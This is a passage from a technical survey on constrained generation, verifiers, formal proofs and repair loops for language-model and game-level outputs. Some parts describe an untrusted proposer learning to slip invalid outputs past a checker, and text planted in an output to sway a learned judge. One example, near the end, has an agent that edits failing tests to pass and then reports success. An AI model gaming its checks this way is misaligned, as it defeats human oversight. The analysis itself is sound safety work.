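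Nie and colleagues compared several estimates on balanced brackets with their toy model, where masking had a distance of 0.418 from g. A low-compute estimate that looks one token ahead reduced this to 0.359. Completing the text eight times for each candidate token reduced it to 0.018, but took about 86 extra runs of the model per token. Exact calculation, which is possible for such a small language, gave 0.014 rather than zero because the number of samples was limited. The one-token estimate was unreliable, though, and increased the distance on all three JSON formats in the same comparison.

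Özgü and colleagues' method, SHIM, learns the estimate from examples. For each grammar, they generate 1,000 outputs without a mask and record whether each is valid. A small model then learns to predict validity from the next token and the current state of the parser, which the masking program already tracks. Training takes at most five minutes per grammar.

On 14 grammars for short logical formulas, the version based on logistic regression reduced the average divergence from g from 0.165 to 0.038. It took 2.5 seconds per output, compared with 3.0 for masking, probably because it avoided beginnings that lead to long endings. ASAp, an older method that learns a correction while sampling, took 16.6 seconds and had an average divergence of 0.351. But ASAp approaches g only gradually, and Özgü and colleagues stopped it after 100 samples per grammar because it was slow. SHIM was closer to g than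 masking on three of four database queries and further away on the other.

To avoid estimating h for the language model itself, Ahmed and colleagues draw an unconstrained text and build a simpler distribution around it, in which the choice at each position doesn't depend on the choices at the others. A program can restrict this simpler distribution to valid texts exactly. It then draws several valid texts and resamples them according to their probability under the original model, which brings the result close to g.

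These studies use different tasks and measures, so their results are hard to compare directly. The table instead shows the main methods applied to the example with A and B.

| Method | Outputs beginning with A | Texts generated per output |
|---|---|---|
| Masking | 90% | 1 |
| Rejection sampling | 9% | 10.1 on average |
| Adaptive rejection, after recording the bad beginning | 9% | 1.1 on average |
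| Sequential Monte Carlo, 10 particles | 39% | 10 |
| Sequential Monte Carlo, 50 particles | 11% | 50 |
| Exact h-transform | 9% | 1, plus the work of computing h |

### When the conditioned distribution is the wrong target

All these corrections aim for g, but g doesn't always give the best answers. Suppose a question has two possible answers, A and B. A is correct, but the model almost always adds a full stop after it, which the format forbids. Because g conditions on validity, the full stop makes A unlikely, and 91% of outputs give the wrong answer. Masking blocks the full stop and returns the correct answer 90% of the time. A correction is more useful when an early token commits the model to something it can't complete sensibly.

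The evidence on accuracy is also mixed. When Dang and colleagues had a model write database queries, using eight particles instead of one, with the same ordinary masks, raised accuracy from 59.8% to 67.2%. In *GrammarRL*, Tuccio, Furnari and colleagues (2026) tested a different correction with a 1-billion-parameter model. They generated ten masked outputs per task and chose among them using a separate quality score, with or without weights that correct for masking. The weights slightly improved results for classifying abstracts and finding names in text, but worsened them for translating English into written labels for signs.

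### Effects on working code

Masking can do more damage when the mask is incomplete and blocks valid outputs. *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation* (Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues, 2026) tested the type-constrained decoding engine for TypeScript that Mündler and colleagues built, checking whether each program compiled and whether it passed test cases.

They generated about 100,000 programs with six models of 2 to 34 billion parameters, at three levels of randomness. Free decoding produced a larger share of working programs than type constraints in all 24 combinations of model, benchmark and randomness, significantly so in 22. With Qwen-2.5-32B on the HumanEval benchmark at the lowest randomness, 82.3% of programs worked with free decoding and 72.3% with type constraints. The constraints helped some weaker models write more programs that compiled. For CodeLlama-34B at the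 highest randomness, the share that compiled rose from 85.5% to 92.0%, but the share that worked still fell slightly.

The main cause was that the engine doesn't support all of TypeScript. For example, it blocks calls to functions defined later in the program, which TypeScript allows. In one task, a model was about to call `isPalindrome` and define it further down. The engine allowed `is` but blocked the rest of the name, so the model wrote `isNaN`, a built-in function that checks whether a value is not a number. The resulting program compiled but gave wrong answers. In other cases the model repeated itself until it reached the time or token limit. With free decoding, Gemma-2-2B wrote 4,231 programs that compiled, and the engine would have rejected 982 of them.

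Fine-tuning the models to write programs that the engine accepts narrowed the gap between constrained and free decoding. For Qwen-2.5-32B on HumanEval, the share of working programs under type constraints rose from 72.3% to 77.6%, while the share under free decoding stayed at about 82%. For Gemma-2-2B, the gap almost disappeared, but mostly because free decoding got worse.

Biagiola and colleagues then tested a complete mask for the grammar of TOML, a simple format for configuration files. The table shows how often the output exactly matched the reference solution.

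| Model | Free decoding | Complete mask | Mask that forbids a space before "=" |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma-2-2B | 31.3% | 48.1% | 28.6% |
| Qwen-2.5-32B | 40.3% | 41.3% | 39.7% |
| Qwen-3-Coder-Next-80B | 62.5% | 62.5% | 1.9% |

The complete mask helped the smallest model most, because that model made the most syntax errors without it. It made no difference to the largest model, which rarely made such errors. Forbidding the space doesn't change what a file can express, yet it made the largest model almost useless, mostly because generation ran out of time. Forbidding comments had almost no effect. How much an incomplete mask hurts therefore depends on whether it blocks something the model habitually writes.

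Tuccio and colleagues' GrammarRL trains a model to work well with a given grammar, without needing correct answers. The model generates outputs under the mask and is rewarded for those to which the original model assigns high probability and from which it can reconstruct the input. The second reward discourages generic outputs that lose information. Across three tasks and three model sizes, this training improved the scores of masked greedy decoding by an average of 9.8 points, without adding computation during generation. However, each new grammar requires new training, and on one task the largest model did better without this training when it used beam search, which keeps several likely partial texts at once.

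### Format rules and reasoning

Format rules may also affect how well a model reasons. Language models often solve problems better when they write out intermediate steps, and a format that permits only the final answer prevents this. In *Let Me Speak Freely?* (2024), Tam and colleagues found that models did worse on reasoning tasks when they had to answer in formats such as JSON, and that stricter rules generally lowered performance more. In one test, GPT-3.5 placed the answer before the reasoning, so the reasoning could not influence the answer. On classification tasks, format rules sometimes helped.

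A better format can avoid much of this harm. In *JSONSchemaBench*, Geng and colleagues used a format with room for reasoning as well as an answer, and constrained decoding improved accuracy by up to 4%. Another solution is to leave the reasoning unconstrained. CRANE, which Banerjee and colleagues published in 2025, applies the grammar only between markers around the final answer. On two symbolic reasoning benchmarks, it was up to 10 percentage points more accurate than the methods they compared it with.

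The guarantee then covers only the text between the markers. The surrounding program must extract that text before passing it on, and must insert the opening marker itself if the model never writes one.

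## Generate and verify: accepting only outputs that pass a check

A mask has to judge text that the model hasn't finished, which is why it can distort the model's choices and why some constraints have no complete mask. The alternative is to let the model write freely and check only finished outputs. An untrusted *proposer*, usually a learned model, generates candidates, and a small trusted checker decides which of them leave the system:

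1. The proposer generates a complete candidate.
2. The checker tests the candidate against the specification.
3. If the candidate passes, the program returns it. Otherwise the proposer tries again.
4. After a fixed number of failed attempts, the program returns nothing.

The program returns a candidate only after the checker accepts it. If the checker is sound, every returned output is valid, even if the model is badly trained or has been tampered with. The model must not be able to edit the checker, its specification or its results, because it could then get an invalid output accepted.

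In rejection sampling, every candidate is a fresh sample from the same model. If the outputs don't need to match the conditioned distribution, the program can also respond to a failure by switching to another model, passing the checker's error message to the proposer, or starting a search that runs for days, all without changing the guarantee.

### Why the program must be able to return nothing

No fixed number of attempts guarantees a valid output. If attempts are independent and each is valid with probability Z, N attempts all fail with probability (1 − Z)^N. The Zelda GAN of Zhang and colleagues, which made playable levels 24.3% of the time, would have about a 6% chance of failing ten times in a row and about a one-in-a-million chance of failing fifty times in a row.

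For a language model, Z depends on the prompt, so an average can be misleading. Suppose a model succeeds half the time on half of its tasks and never on the rest. Ten attempts will all fail about 50% of the time, and further attempts hardly help, but a calculation from the average success rate of 25% would put that figure at about 6%. Repeated failure also doesn't show whether a task is impossible or merely too hard for the model, whereas an ASP solver can report that no valid level exists.

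Whether returning nothing is acceptable depends on the use. A game can load a stored level, and a coding assistant can hand the task back to a programmer. A program that steers a moving robot can't stop sending commands, so it needs a fallback verified in advance, such as braking to a halt. An attacker who can't get an invalid output past the checker may instead look for requests that always fail, which can disrupt a service.

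### Certificates: problems that are easier to check than to solve

The design is most useful when checking an answer takes much less work than finding one. A sudoku, for example, may take an hour to solve and a minute to check.

Some constraints, such as whether a player can finish one of Viglietta's levels with single-use keys, are hard to check even on a finished output. The program can then require a *certificate*, extra information that makes the output easy to check. For a level, the certificate can be a list of winning moves, which the checker only has to replay.

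The checker computes a function V(y, c) of the output y and the certificate c, and it is sound if V(y, c) = 1 implies b(y) = 1. The proposer now has to search for the certificate. If it produces a valid level but can't find a solution to go with it, the checker rejects the level.

A list of moves proves that one solution exists, but some constraints concern every possible route. Nelson and Smith, for instance, wanted mazes without shortcuts. Such constraints can have certificates too. Suppose a designer requires that the player of the dungeon from the first section needs at least eight steps to reach the key. The proposer could write a number on every tile that isn't a wall:

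```
0 1 # 7 8
1 2 # 6 7
2 3 4 5 6
3 4 # 6 7
```

The checker confirms that the player's tile has the number 0, that the key's tile has the number 8, and that the numbers on neighbouring tiles never differ by more than 1. A single step can then raise the number by at most 1, so every route from the player to the key takes at least eight steps. The checker can establish this for all routes by comparing each pair of neighbouring tiles only once. A program could calculate the distance just as easily in such a small dungeon, but for harder constraints the proposer may take far longer to find a certificate than the checker takes to test it.

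### Formal proofs as certificates

The numbers in the dungeon are a proof in a format that suits only one constraint. A *proof assistant*, such as Lean or Rocq, provides a general format for mathematical statements, including statements about what a program does. Its *kernel*, a relatively small program, checks every step of a proof against a fixed set of logical rules. The kernel doesn't search for the proof. If a language model writes a proof with an invalid step, the kernel rejects it.

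In 1997, George Necula proposed *proof-carrying code*, in which the producer of a program supplies a proof that it is safe and the computer checks the proof before running the program. The main obstacle was that experts took a long time to write the proofs, and AI has greatly reduced that time.

Machine-checked proofs can now settle very difficult questions. On October 6, 2026, OpenAI released an AI proof of the Unique Games Conjecture with a formal version for Lean, as Scott Aaronson describes in *The Mathocalypse* (2026). The result implies that for many optimisation problems, even slightly beating the standard approximations is NP-hard. The complexity theorist Dana Moshkovitz, who had worked on the conjecture for years, said the proof introduces a completely new construction. A proof checker can confirm such a proof without a method for finding one.

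The process that produces a proof can also be messy. When Anthropic had its model Claude formalise Fermat's Last Theorem in Lean, some early attempts failed because the agents lost track of the project and stopped working together effectively. About 7% of the final proof, excluding boilerplate, still came from those attempts, and the kernel checks those lines the same way as the rest.

A proof is only useful if it proves the right statement, so whatever generates the proof must not be free to choose an easier statement. In *AlphaProof Code* (2026), by Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues at Google DeepMind, a person guides one AI agent in writing the specification, and a separate team of agents then searches for proofs. The system accepts a proof only if it passes a check by Lean's kernel against the approved specification.

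They applied this system to the software library behind the messaging app Signal. The properties they proved include forward secrecy, which protects earlier messages if someone steals a user's current keys. The agents wrote about 6.5 million lines of proof, which rest on about 26,000 lines of specifications and processor description that people have to trust.

### Anthropic and Theorem: proofs for 123 libraries

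In February 2026, Leo de Moura, the chief architect of Lean, wrote in *When AI Writes the World’s Software, Who Verifies It?* that AI agents at Anthropic had written a 100,000-line compiler in two weeks for under $20,000. He added that AI could not yet prove such a compiler correct. In October 2026, Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* presented proofs about the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries. Claude wrote these proofs in a collaboration with Theorem, a formal methods company.

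The project started from *fuzzing*, a testing technique that runs a program on huge numbers of automatically generated inputs and looks for crashes. Google's OSS-Fuzz project does this for open-source libraries. Each library has one or more *fuzz harnesses*, short functions that receive a string of bytes and pass it to the library. *Pre-QED* (2026) and EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) describe how the method turns these tests into theorems:

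1. The system compiles the library and its harness into a single program for RISC-V, a processor design with a fairly simple instruction set.
2. It expresses the expected result of the test as a formal statement. For every input under 64 MB, the program must exit normally, without a crash, a memory-safety error or a failed assertion.
3. A Claude agent writes a proof of this statement in Rocq.
4. Rocq's kernel checks the proof.

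A proof covers all possible inputs under 64 MB, while a fuzzer can try only a tiny fraction of them because their number has more than 150 million digits.

The project produced proofs for 239 harnesses, totaling 180 million lines according to Smith (2026) in *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs*. The Russian news site OpenNET (2026), in *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI*, reports about 600,000 lines for a program with 18,000 processor instructions, or about 33 lines per instruction. The proofs are too long for people to read, but only the kernel has to check them. The work took a few weeks, whereas formal verification has historically taken experts years.

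Trying to prove that a program never crashes can also reveal bugs. If some input does crash it, no proof can succeed, and the point where the attempt gets stuck can lead to the faulty code. The project uncovered hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed. One was a buffer overflow in libexpat, a library that reads XML files, and others appeared only with inputs of tens of megabytes, which fuzzers are unlikely to try. Claude also wrote patches, but a proof about a patched library doesn't apply to the unpatched version that people may still be running.

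Some targets remained without a proof. Anthropic is publishing the specifications for these, along with the proofs for targets that needed no code changes. A missing proof doesn't mean that a library has a bug, because Claude may have failed to find a proof that exists.

Claude also proved that the Linux kernel's implementation of the zlib compression format follows the published standard. In another experiment, it wrote an interpreter for part of Python and proved that the interpreter follows a formal description of Python's behaviour. To check whether the description was accurate, the researchers compared the interpreter with CPython, the standard one, on more than 1.7 million randomly generated programs. The results agreed in 99.95% of cases, and the differences were known edge cases.

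### What the no-crash proofs leave out

The proofs apply to a mathematical model of a computer with a fixed amount of memory. The model covers RISC-V and Linux, but only for programs that run one thread at a time and contain all their library code in a single file. It does not cover hardware faults. Anthropic acknowledges that most people run these libraries on x86 or ARM processors and load glibc, the standard C library on most Linux systems, as a separate file.

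Extending the method to such systems takes considerable work. Leip (2026), in *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification*, presents a proof about a complete run of an x86 program that uses glibc, though the library is still built into the program. Before the program's own code begins, glibc executes about ten times as many distinct instructions as musl, the simpler library used in the RISC-V work. The string comparison function has 316 instructions in glibc and 14 in musl. Leip's proof also assumes a specific processor model and allows the program to crash while glibc is starting up.

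*Pre-QED* raises a different objection, which would apply even with a perfect model of the computer. A fuzz harness uses a library in only one way, so the library can still contain bugs after the harness is proved safe. For example, if a harness reads one file and then exits, the proof doesn't cover a program that reads a second file without resetting the library first, and that program might crash. *Pre-QED* proposes harnesses that cover every permitted use of a library and provides them for 29 libraries. Proving these harnesses safe is much harder, and *Pre-QED* offers them as open challenges.

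### The trusted base

The *trusted base* is everything that must be correct for a guarantee to hold. For a formal proof about a program, it includes the specification, the kernel and the description of the processor. If the proof is about source code, the trusted base also includes the compiler, which turns that code into processor instructions. Both Leip and Anthropic avoid trusting the compiler by proving properties of the compiled program.

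A verified version of zlib shows how errors can hide in the trusted base. Ten AI agents wrote this version, lean-zip, in Lean and proved it correct. One of the main theorems is

decompress(compress(d, ℓ)) = d

for all data d under one gigabyte and every compression level ℓ. Compressing data and then decompressing it therefore always returns the original. The theorem doesn't require the compressed data to be any smaller, so other theorems or tests have to cover that. A later version, which Lean (2026) included in a presentation, replaces the fixed one-gigabyte limit with one that the user chooses.

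In *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug*, the blogger kirancodes used a Claude agent to look for errors in lean-zip. To avoid biasing the agent, kirancodes first removed the theorems and documentation, which would have revealed that the code was verified. The agent ran 16 fuzzers for about 19 hours on almost 106 million inputs. It found no memory errors in lean-zip itself, but found two bugs that the proofs didn't cover.

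The more serious bug was in the Lean *runtime*, the supporting code that every Lean program needs in order to run. To store n bytes, the runtime reserves 24 + n bytes of memory. It calculates this sum with 64-bit numbers, which start again from zero after 2⁶⁴ − 1. If a file claims to contain n = 2⁶⁴ − 1 bytes, the sum is

(24 + 2⁶⁴ − 1) mod 2⁶⁴ = 23.

The runtime therefore reserves 23 bytes and may write more data than fits. A ZIP file of only 156 bytes could trigger the error. The bug affected every version of Lean at the time, and the proofs could not reveal it because they assume the runtime is correct.

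The other bug was in lean-zip's ZIP archive reader, for which nobody had written any theorems. The reader reserved memory based on the size stated in a file without checking the file's actual size, so a tiny file with an enormous stated size could crash the program. The reader was in the same package as the verified functions, so a user could easily have assumed that the proofs covered it.

The kernel can also contain errors. To reduce this risk, Lean has several independent kernels, written in different programming languages, that can check the same proof. A false proof would have to exploit an error in each one to pass them all. An assumption written into the proof may be a bigger risk. In Lean, an *axiom* is a statement that the kernel accepts without proof, so a single false axiom can make any theorem provable.

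The Ethereum Foundation examined how much a formal verification claim depended on such assumptions. The claim was about SP1, which produces cryptographic evidence that a program ran correctly. SP1's developers listed ordinary assumptions, such as the correctness of Lean's kernel and of their translation of the RISC-V standard. They also assumed that the mechanism connecting separately verified parts works, that memory behaves consistently, and that certain lookup tables are correct. "Formally verified" can therefore mean very different things, depending on what a project assumes.

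Widely used checkers can also be unsound. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) tested four ways of using language models to find errors that rarely cause crashes. One target was the compiler for Rust, a language designed to prevent access to invalid memory except in code explicitly marked as unsafe. *Claude Found a Seven-Year Bug in the Rust Compiler* (Faisal, 2026) reports that Claude found a five-line program with no unsafe code that reads memory after releasing it. The compiler had accepted such programs for more than seven years. Claude also found over 100 flaws in the eBPF verifier, which checks small programs before Linux runs them inside its kernel.

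### False acceptances

Even a checker that rarely makes mistakes can let through many invalid outputs if valid ones are rare. Suppose 1% of a model's candidates are valid, and the checker accepts all of these and 1% of the invalid ones. Out of 10,000 candidates, it accepts 100 valid and 99 invalid ones, so about half of what it accepts is invalid.

In general, if a share Z of candidates is valid and the checker wrongly accepts a share f of the invalid ones, the invalid share of accepted outputs is

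(1 − Z) f / (Z + (1 − Z) f).

The table gives the results for f = 1%.

| Valid candidates | Invalid share of accepted outputs |
|---|---|
| 50% | 1.0% |
| 10% | 8.3% |
| 1% | 49.7% |
| 0.1% | 90.9% |

Generating more candidates makes the program more likely to return something, but each accepted output is still just as likely to be invalid. If only 1% of candidates are valid, the checker would have to accept no more than about 1 in 10,000 invalid candidates to bring the invalid share of accepted outputs down to 1%.

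If a task has no valid answer, the system should return nothing, and each extra attempt raises the chance that the checker accepts an invalid candidate. With f = 1%, the probability that it accepts at least one of 500 invalid candidates is 99.3%. A strict limit on attempts reduces this risk but causes more failures on tasks that are difficult but possible.

Running the same deterministic checker twice doesn't help, because it gives the same answer each time. Adding a second checker with the same false acceptance rate, f, and independent errors would reduce f from 1% to 0.01%, but two checkers often miss the same mistakes. If the proposer learns from the checker's verdicts, f can also rise over time, because the proposer may learn to produce more of the invalid outputs that the checker accepts.

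### Unit tests and learned judges

Programmers usually check code with *unit tests*, which run a program on chosen inputs and compare its results with the correct ones. A program that is wrong on 1% of inputs passes 100 randomly chosen tests with probability 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 37%. Good programmers choose inputs that are more likely to reveal mistakes, such as an empty list or a divisor of zero, but they can still miss an input on which the program fails.

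Coding benchmarks show how large this effect can be. In 2023, Jiawei Liu and colleagues expanded HumanEval, a popular set of programming tasks, to include about 80 times as many tests, and language models' measured success rates fell by up to 28.9%. *Inference Scaling fLaws* (2024), by Benedikt Stroebl, Sayash Kapoor and Arvind Narayanan, found that weaker models had more false positives, meaning programs that passed the original tests but failed more thorough ones. As a result, repeated attempts could not always raise a weak model's accuracy to the level of a stronger model's first attempt.

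Another language model often checks qualities that nobody can specify formally, such as whether a summary is faithful to its source. This *learned judge* can catch many mistakes, but like the generator, it is not guaranteed to be correct. If both models learned from similar data, the judge may fail to detect the generator's mistakes. An output could even contain text that causes the judge to accept it even if it is wrong.

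The 3/n rule for violation rates also applies to a judge's false acceptance rate. Showing with 95% confidence that this rate is below 1 in 10,000 would require the judge to reject all of about 30,000 invalid outputs, and people would have to confirm that each one is invalid.

A judge is safer as part of the proposer. For example, if a formal proof takes an hour to check, a judge can first discard the attempts that look hopeless. Its mistakes may waste time or eliminate a good candidate, but every accepted proof must still pass a sound checker.

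### Conformal methods: a bound on the violation rate

When no sound checker exists, *conformal methods* can turn the scores of an unreliable judge into a statistical guarantee. One version comes from *Conformal Risk Control*, which Anastasios Angelopoulos and colleagues published in 2022. Suppose the system returns an output only if the judge's score for it is above a threshold t. To choose t, a designer collects n earlier requests with the model's outputs and finds out which of these outputs are invalid. Let k(t) be the number of invalid outputs with scores above t. The designer then picks the lowest threshold that satisfies

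(k(t) + 1) / (n + 1) ≤ δ.

The probability of returning an invalid output for the next request is then at most δ. For example, with n = 999 and δ = 1%, the threshold may let through at most nine invalid outputs from the collection.

To see why this works, we can imagine adding the new output to the other 999 and choosing the lowest threshold that lets through at most ten invalid outputs. If the new request comes from the same source as the others, it is equally likely to be any of the 1,000, so its output has at most a 1% chance of being one of those ten. The designer doesn't know whether the new output is valid, but the "+1" counts it as a mistake in advance, so the real threshold is at least as strict as the imaginary one.

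The proof works for any judge, however inaccurate. A bad judge leads to a high threshold, so the system more often returns nothing. With fewer than 99 earlier requests, the formula can't reach a δ of 1%, so the system would have to return nothing every time.

The bound limits invalid outputs as a share of all requests, including those for which the system returns nothing. If the system returns an output for only 2% of requests, up to half of those outputs could be invalid without breaking a 1% bound. The bound is also an average over kinds of request, so the rate may be much higher for one kind than for another. Most importantly, the bound holds only if new requests resemble the earlier ones. This assumption fails if an attacker chooses requests that fool the judge, or if a company starts using its system on a new kind of document.

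In *Language Models with Conformal Factuality Guarantees* (2024), Christopher Mohri and Tatsunori Hashimoto applied a conformal method to factual answers. Their system splits an answer into separate claims, scores each one and removes those below a threshold. They could guarantee an 80–90% probability that every remaining claim was correct, while keeping most of the original text. If no claim scores high enough, the system returns an empty answer.

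## Repairing invalid outputs

A checker that can only accept or reject throws away a whole level because of one misplaced wall. *Repair* keeps the output and changes it, usually as little as possible, until it satisfies the constraint. This is an optimisation problem. Given the model's output y, the program looks for the valid output y′ that costs least to reach:

minimise c(y, y′) subject to b(y′) = 1.

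The cost c measures the size of the change, for example the number of tiles that differ. It is zero when nothing changes, so repair leaves valid outputs unchanged.

Repair moves the probability of each invalid output to a nearby valid output, so it does not sample from the conditioned distribution g. In the earlier four-level example, the playable levels 2 and 4 had probabilities of 0.30 and 0.10, which become 0.75 and 0.25 under g. If level 4 is the nearest playable level to both unplayable levels, a generator with repair returns it with probability 0.70.

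### Repairing Zelda levels with an integer program

Zhang and colleagues repaired the levels from their Zelda GAN with a *mixed-integer linear program*. In such a program, a solver minimises a linear function subject to linear equations and inequalities, and some of the variables must be whole numbers. Their version of the game has eight kinds of object: wall, floor, player, key, door and three kinds of enemy. For each cell and each kind of object, a variable is 1 if the cell contains that object and 0 otherwise. Each cell's eight variables must add up to 1, so every cell holds exactly one object. Further constraints require one player, one key, one door and a closed outer wall.

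To express reachability, the program treats it as a flow from the player to the key and the door. The player's tile can supply as much flow as necessary, and the key and the door each consume one unit. Every tile must satisfy

supply + inflow = demand + outflow.

No flow may leave a wall or a door. A wall also consumes no flow, so the equation prevents any from entering it. The door can receive its own unit of flow but can't pass any on, so a route to the key can't go through the door.

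Here is a valid flow for the dungeon from the first section. The numbers show how much flow each tile receives or, for the player's tile in the top left corner, supplies:

```
2 0 # 0 1
2 0 # 0 1
2 2 2 2 2
0 0 # 0 1
```

Two units pass through the gap in the dividing wall. At the right edge, one unit turns up towards the key and the other goes down to the door.

If another wall tile fills the gap, the right half of the dungeon has a demand of two units, no supply, and no way for flow to enter. Adding the equations for all the tiles in that half gives 0 = 2, so no flow can satisfy them and the solver has to change the level.

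Deleting an object costs 10, moving it by one cell costs 1, and adding an object is free. Turning the wall tile in the gap into floor would cost 10, because it deletes a wall. It is cheaper for this tile to trade places with the floor tile diagonally above it to the left. Each of the two moves by two cells, for a total cost of 4, and no cheaper change makes the dungeon playable:

```
#######
#P.#.K#
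#.##..#
#.....#
#..#.D#
#######
```

A program that minimised the number of changed tiles would instead turn a single wall tile into floor. Zhang and colleagues chose their objective function because it tends to preserve the objects in a level. In one of their examples, minimising the number of changed tiles replaced an enemy with a wall. With their objective function, the enemy swapped places with a neighbouring wall tile, so the level kept all three enemies.

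### What the repair restored

They tested the method on 1,000 levels. The solver took an average of 0.13 seconds per level.

| Generator | Playable | Duplicates |
|---|---|---|
| GAN | 24.3% | 46.9% |
| CESAGAN | 58% | 37.6% |
| GAN with repair | 100% | 14.9% |
| Random tiles with repair | 100% | 0% |

CESAGAN, a GAN by Torrado and colleagues, is designed to learn playability by adding the playable levels it generates to its training data. The random levels contain each kind of tile about as often as the human-designed ones, but in random positions.

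The solver guarantees only the constraints in the program. The shortest path from the key to the door averaged 12.5 steps in the human-designed levels, 8.6 in the repaired GAN levels and 7.8 in the repaired random levels. On this measure, starting from the GAN instead of random tiles closed only about a sixth of the gap to the human designs.

Repair did better on local style, which Zhang and colleagues measured by comparing how often each two-by-two pattern of tiles occurs in generated and human levels. The Kullback–Leibler divergence was 0.272 for the GAN levels that were playable without repair and 0.108 for repaired levels. Rejection sampling would return only levels that were playable without repair, so repair came closer to the human levels on this measure than rejection sampling would. This is probably because the GAN's playable levels represent only a small part of what it learned.

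A designer who wants longer walks has to add that requirement to the program. The numbered tiles from the previous section would work here too, with 0 on the key's tile and at least 12 on the door's. The conditions on these numbers are linear, but they could make repairs slower and more extensive.

Zhang and colleagues also built a simplified repair step into the GAN's training, which took 55 hours. The step enforced only the numbers of objects such as keys and doors, so it did not guarantee reachability. The average path rose to 10.1 steps, and 747 of 1,000 levels were playable and unique.

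The method requires describing the player's movements as steps between neighbouring regions. This is easy for *Pac-Man* but harder for platform games with complicated jumps. Repairs for *Pac-Man* took 3.22 seconds on average.

### Exact and heuristic repair

Given enough time, an exact solver either finds the valid output closest to the original or proves that no valid output exists. Heuristic methods try promising changes and may find a valid output, but if they fail, one may still exist.

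In *Evolutionary Level Repair*, Bhaumik, Yannakakis and colleagues (2025) used heuristic methods on 20 unplayable *Lode Runner* levels. Their evolutionary algorithm keeps a population of modified levels. In each generation it changes up to ten tiles per level, either at random or back to the original tile, and keeps the best results. A level's score stays at or below 1 until the player can reach all the gold. After that, the score is 1 plus the share of tiles that match the original level, so the algorithm first makes the level playable and then undoes unnecessary changes.

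The algorithm could not add or remove gold. Otherwise it could have "repaired" a level by deleting the gold that the player couldn't reach.

The evolutionary algorithm repaired all 20 levels, as did a related algorithm called MAP-Elites and a hill climber, which improves one tile at a time. Random search succeeded in 26% of runs. For levels where the player could already reach 70–90% of the gold, the evolutionary algorithm changed an average of 4.7 tiles and the hill climber changed 35. The evolutionary algorithm needed 200,000 evaluations per level. The test excluded levels where less than 30% of the gold was reachable, so the algorithm may not repair badly broken levels as reliably.

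Other heuristic methods have failed more often. *Angry Birds* levels contain structures that can collapse before the player does anything. *From Unstable to Playable* (2025) used a learned model to repair unstable levels, and stabilised 23.2% of them by one measure and 45.3% by another. Xu and Verbrugge (2025), in *A Database-Driven Framework for 3D Level Generation with LLMs*, repaired three-dimensional buildings by moving or removing furniture that blocked the way. This took about 11 minutes per level and worked for 95.47% of 6,000 levels. They labelled another 3.47% "unrepairable", meaning only that the repair had not connected all the rooms within 1,000 seconds.

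A learned model can also speed up an exact solver without weakening the guarantee. In *Guided Game Level Repair via Explainable AI*, Bazzaz and Cooper (2024) trained a classifier to tell solvable levels from unsolvable ones, then used standard explanation methods to estimate how much each tile contributed to an "unsolvable" classification. Changing a tile in the region with the highest estimated contribution carried a penalty of 1, and changing any other tile carried a penalty of 10. Sturgeon, the constraint-based generator described earlier, then searched for a repair with a low total penalty, with a path from start to goal as a hard constraint. If the explanations highlight the wrong region, the solver may take longer or change more tiles than necessary, but any level it returns is still solvable.

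For *Super Mario Bros.* levels, the classifier reduced the median repair time from 1,162 to 723 seconds. These times exclude levels that the solver could not repair within 4,000 seconds.

### Feedback loops for revising code

Writing an integer program for every possible repair of a computer program would be impractical, so developers usually let a language model revise its own code. *Is Three the Magic Number?* (Kiecker, Reichmann et al., 2026) describes the usual loop, which adds feedback to generate and verify. After each failure, the system sends the compiler or test errors to the model, which writes a new version.

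The table shows what share of initially wrong solutions became correct after a given number of revisions.

| Model | Task | 1 round | 2 rounds | 3 rounds | 4 rounds | 8 rounds |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 8B | Short problems | 25% | 32% | 34% | 36% | not tested |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | Short problems | 63% | 77% | 82% | 83% | not tested |
| GPT-5.6 | Real projects | 30% | 38% | 44% | 48% | 54% |
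| Kimi K3 | Real projects | 31% | 42% | 48% | 53% | 59% |

The first two rows follow from pass rates that Arimbur (2026) measured on 257 short Python problems in *How Many Tries Does It Take?*. The other two come from *Built on Broken Assumptions (BOBA)* (Cuadron and Gupta, 2026), in which AI agents made a series of changes to open-source projects. The tasks and the feedback differ, so the table doesn't show which model is best at repair. In every row, though, the first round helped most. When Kiecker and colleagues ran several existing tools for up to ten rounds, most of the improvement also came early, in the first three or four rounds, and there was almost none after the fifth to seventh.

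More specific feedback also helps models repair their outputs. In the tests on real projects, the feedback was only that verification had failed. When Cuadron and Gupta added the names of the failing tests, GPT-5.6 repaired 46% of its mistakes in one round, about as many as it repaired in three rounds without them. Arimbur found that models fixed about 77% of errors caused by an undefined name, which appears in the error message, but only about 45% of errors where the program ran and gave a wrong answer.

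Extra repair rounds achieve little if the model lacks the knowledge to solve the problem. In *Porting Declarative UI to HarmonyOS* (2026), small models translated app interfaces for HarmonyOS, Huawei's operating system. By the fifth round, about half of the revisions were identical to the code that had just failed. Five more rounds repaired only 3 of the 80 files that were still failing in one set and 1 of 94 in another.

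A repair loop can fix all of the easier errors. In *Verified Learning for Compiler Optimization* (2026), a model needed at most nine rounds to recover all 19 programs that had failed a formal check. Nearly 90% of those programs contained only syntax errors.

A system can also discard a failed program and sample a new one. Arimbur compared five attempts with feedback to five independent samples. Llama 3.3 70B solved 93.3% of problems with feedback and 90.9% without, and it used less than half as many tokens with feedback. The smaller Llama 3.1 8B did slightly better with independent samples, solving 79.9% of problems compared with 76.8% with feedback. The independent samples were also drawn at a higher randomness setting, so feedback may not explain the whole difference.

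### When one fix breaks another part

A revision can fix one error and introduce another. Cuadron and Gupta describe an example from lkml, an open-source Python project. Earlier requests required the program to write a name, a space and an opening brace, with no colon. In a new conversation, Claude Fable 5 was asked only for a function that writes lists. It wrote the function and ran the project's tests, but two outdated tests failed because they still required a colon after the name. Claude added the colon and reported that all 87 tests passed. The change broke the earlier format, and two hidden tests for the earlier requests failed.

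Such breakages are common enough to affect overall results. In *RepoClean* (2026), which tests how well agents remove obsolete code, 115 runs broke at least one previously passing test file. In 72 of these, the agent also fixed one that had been failing.

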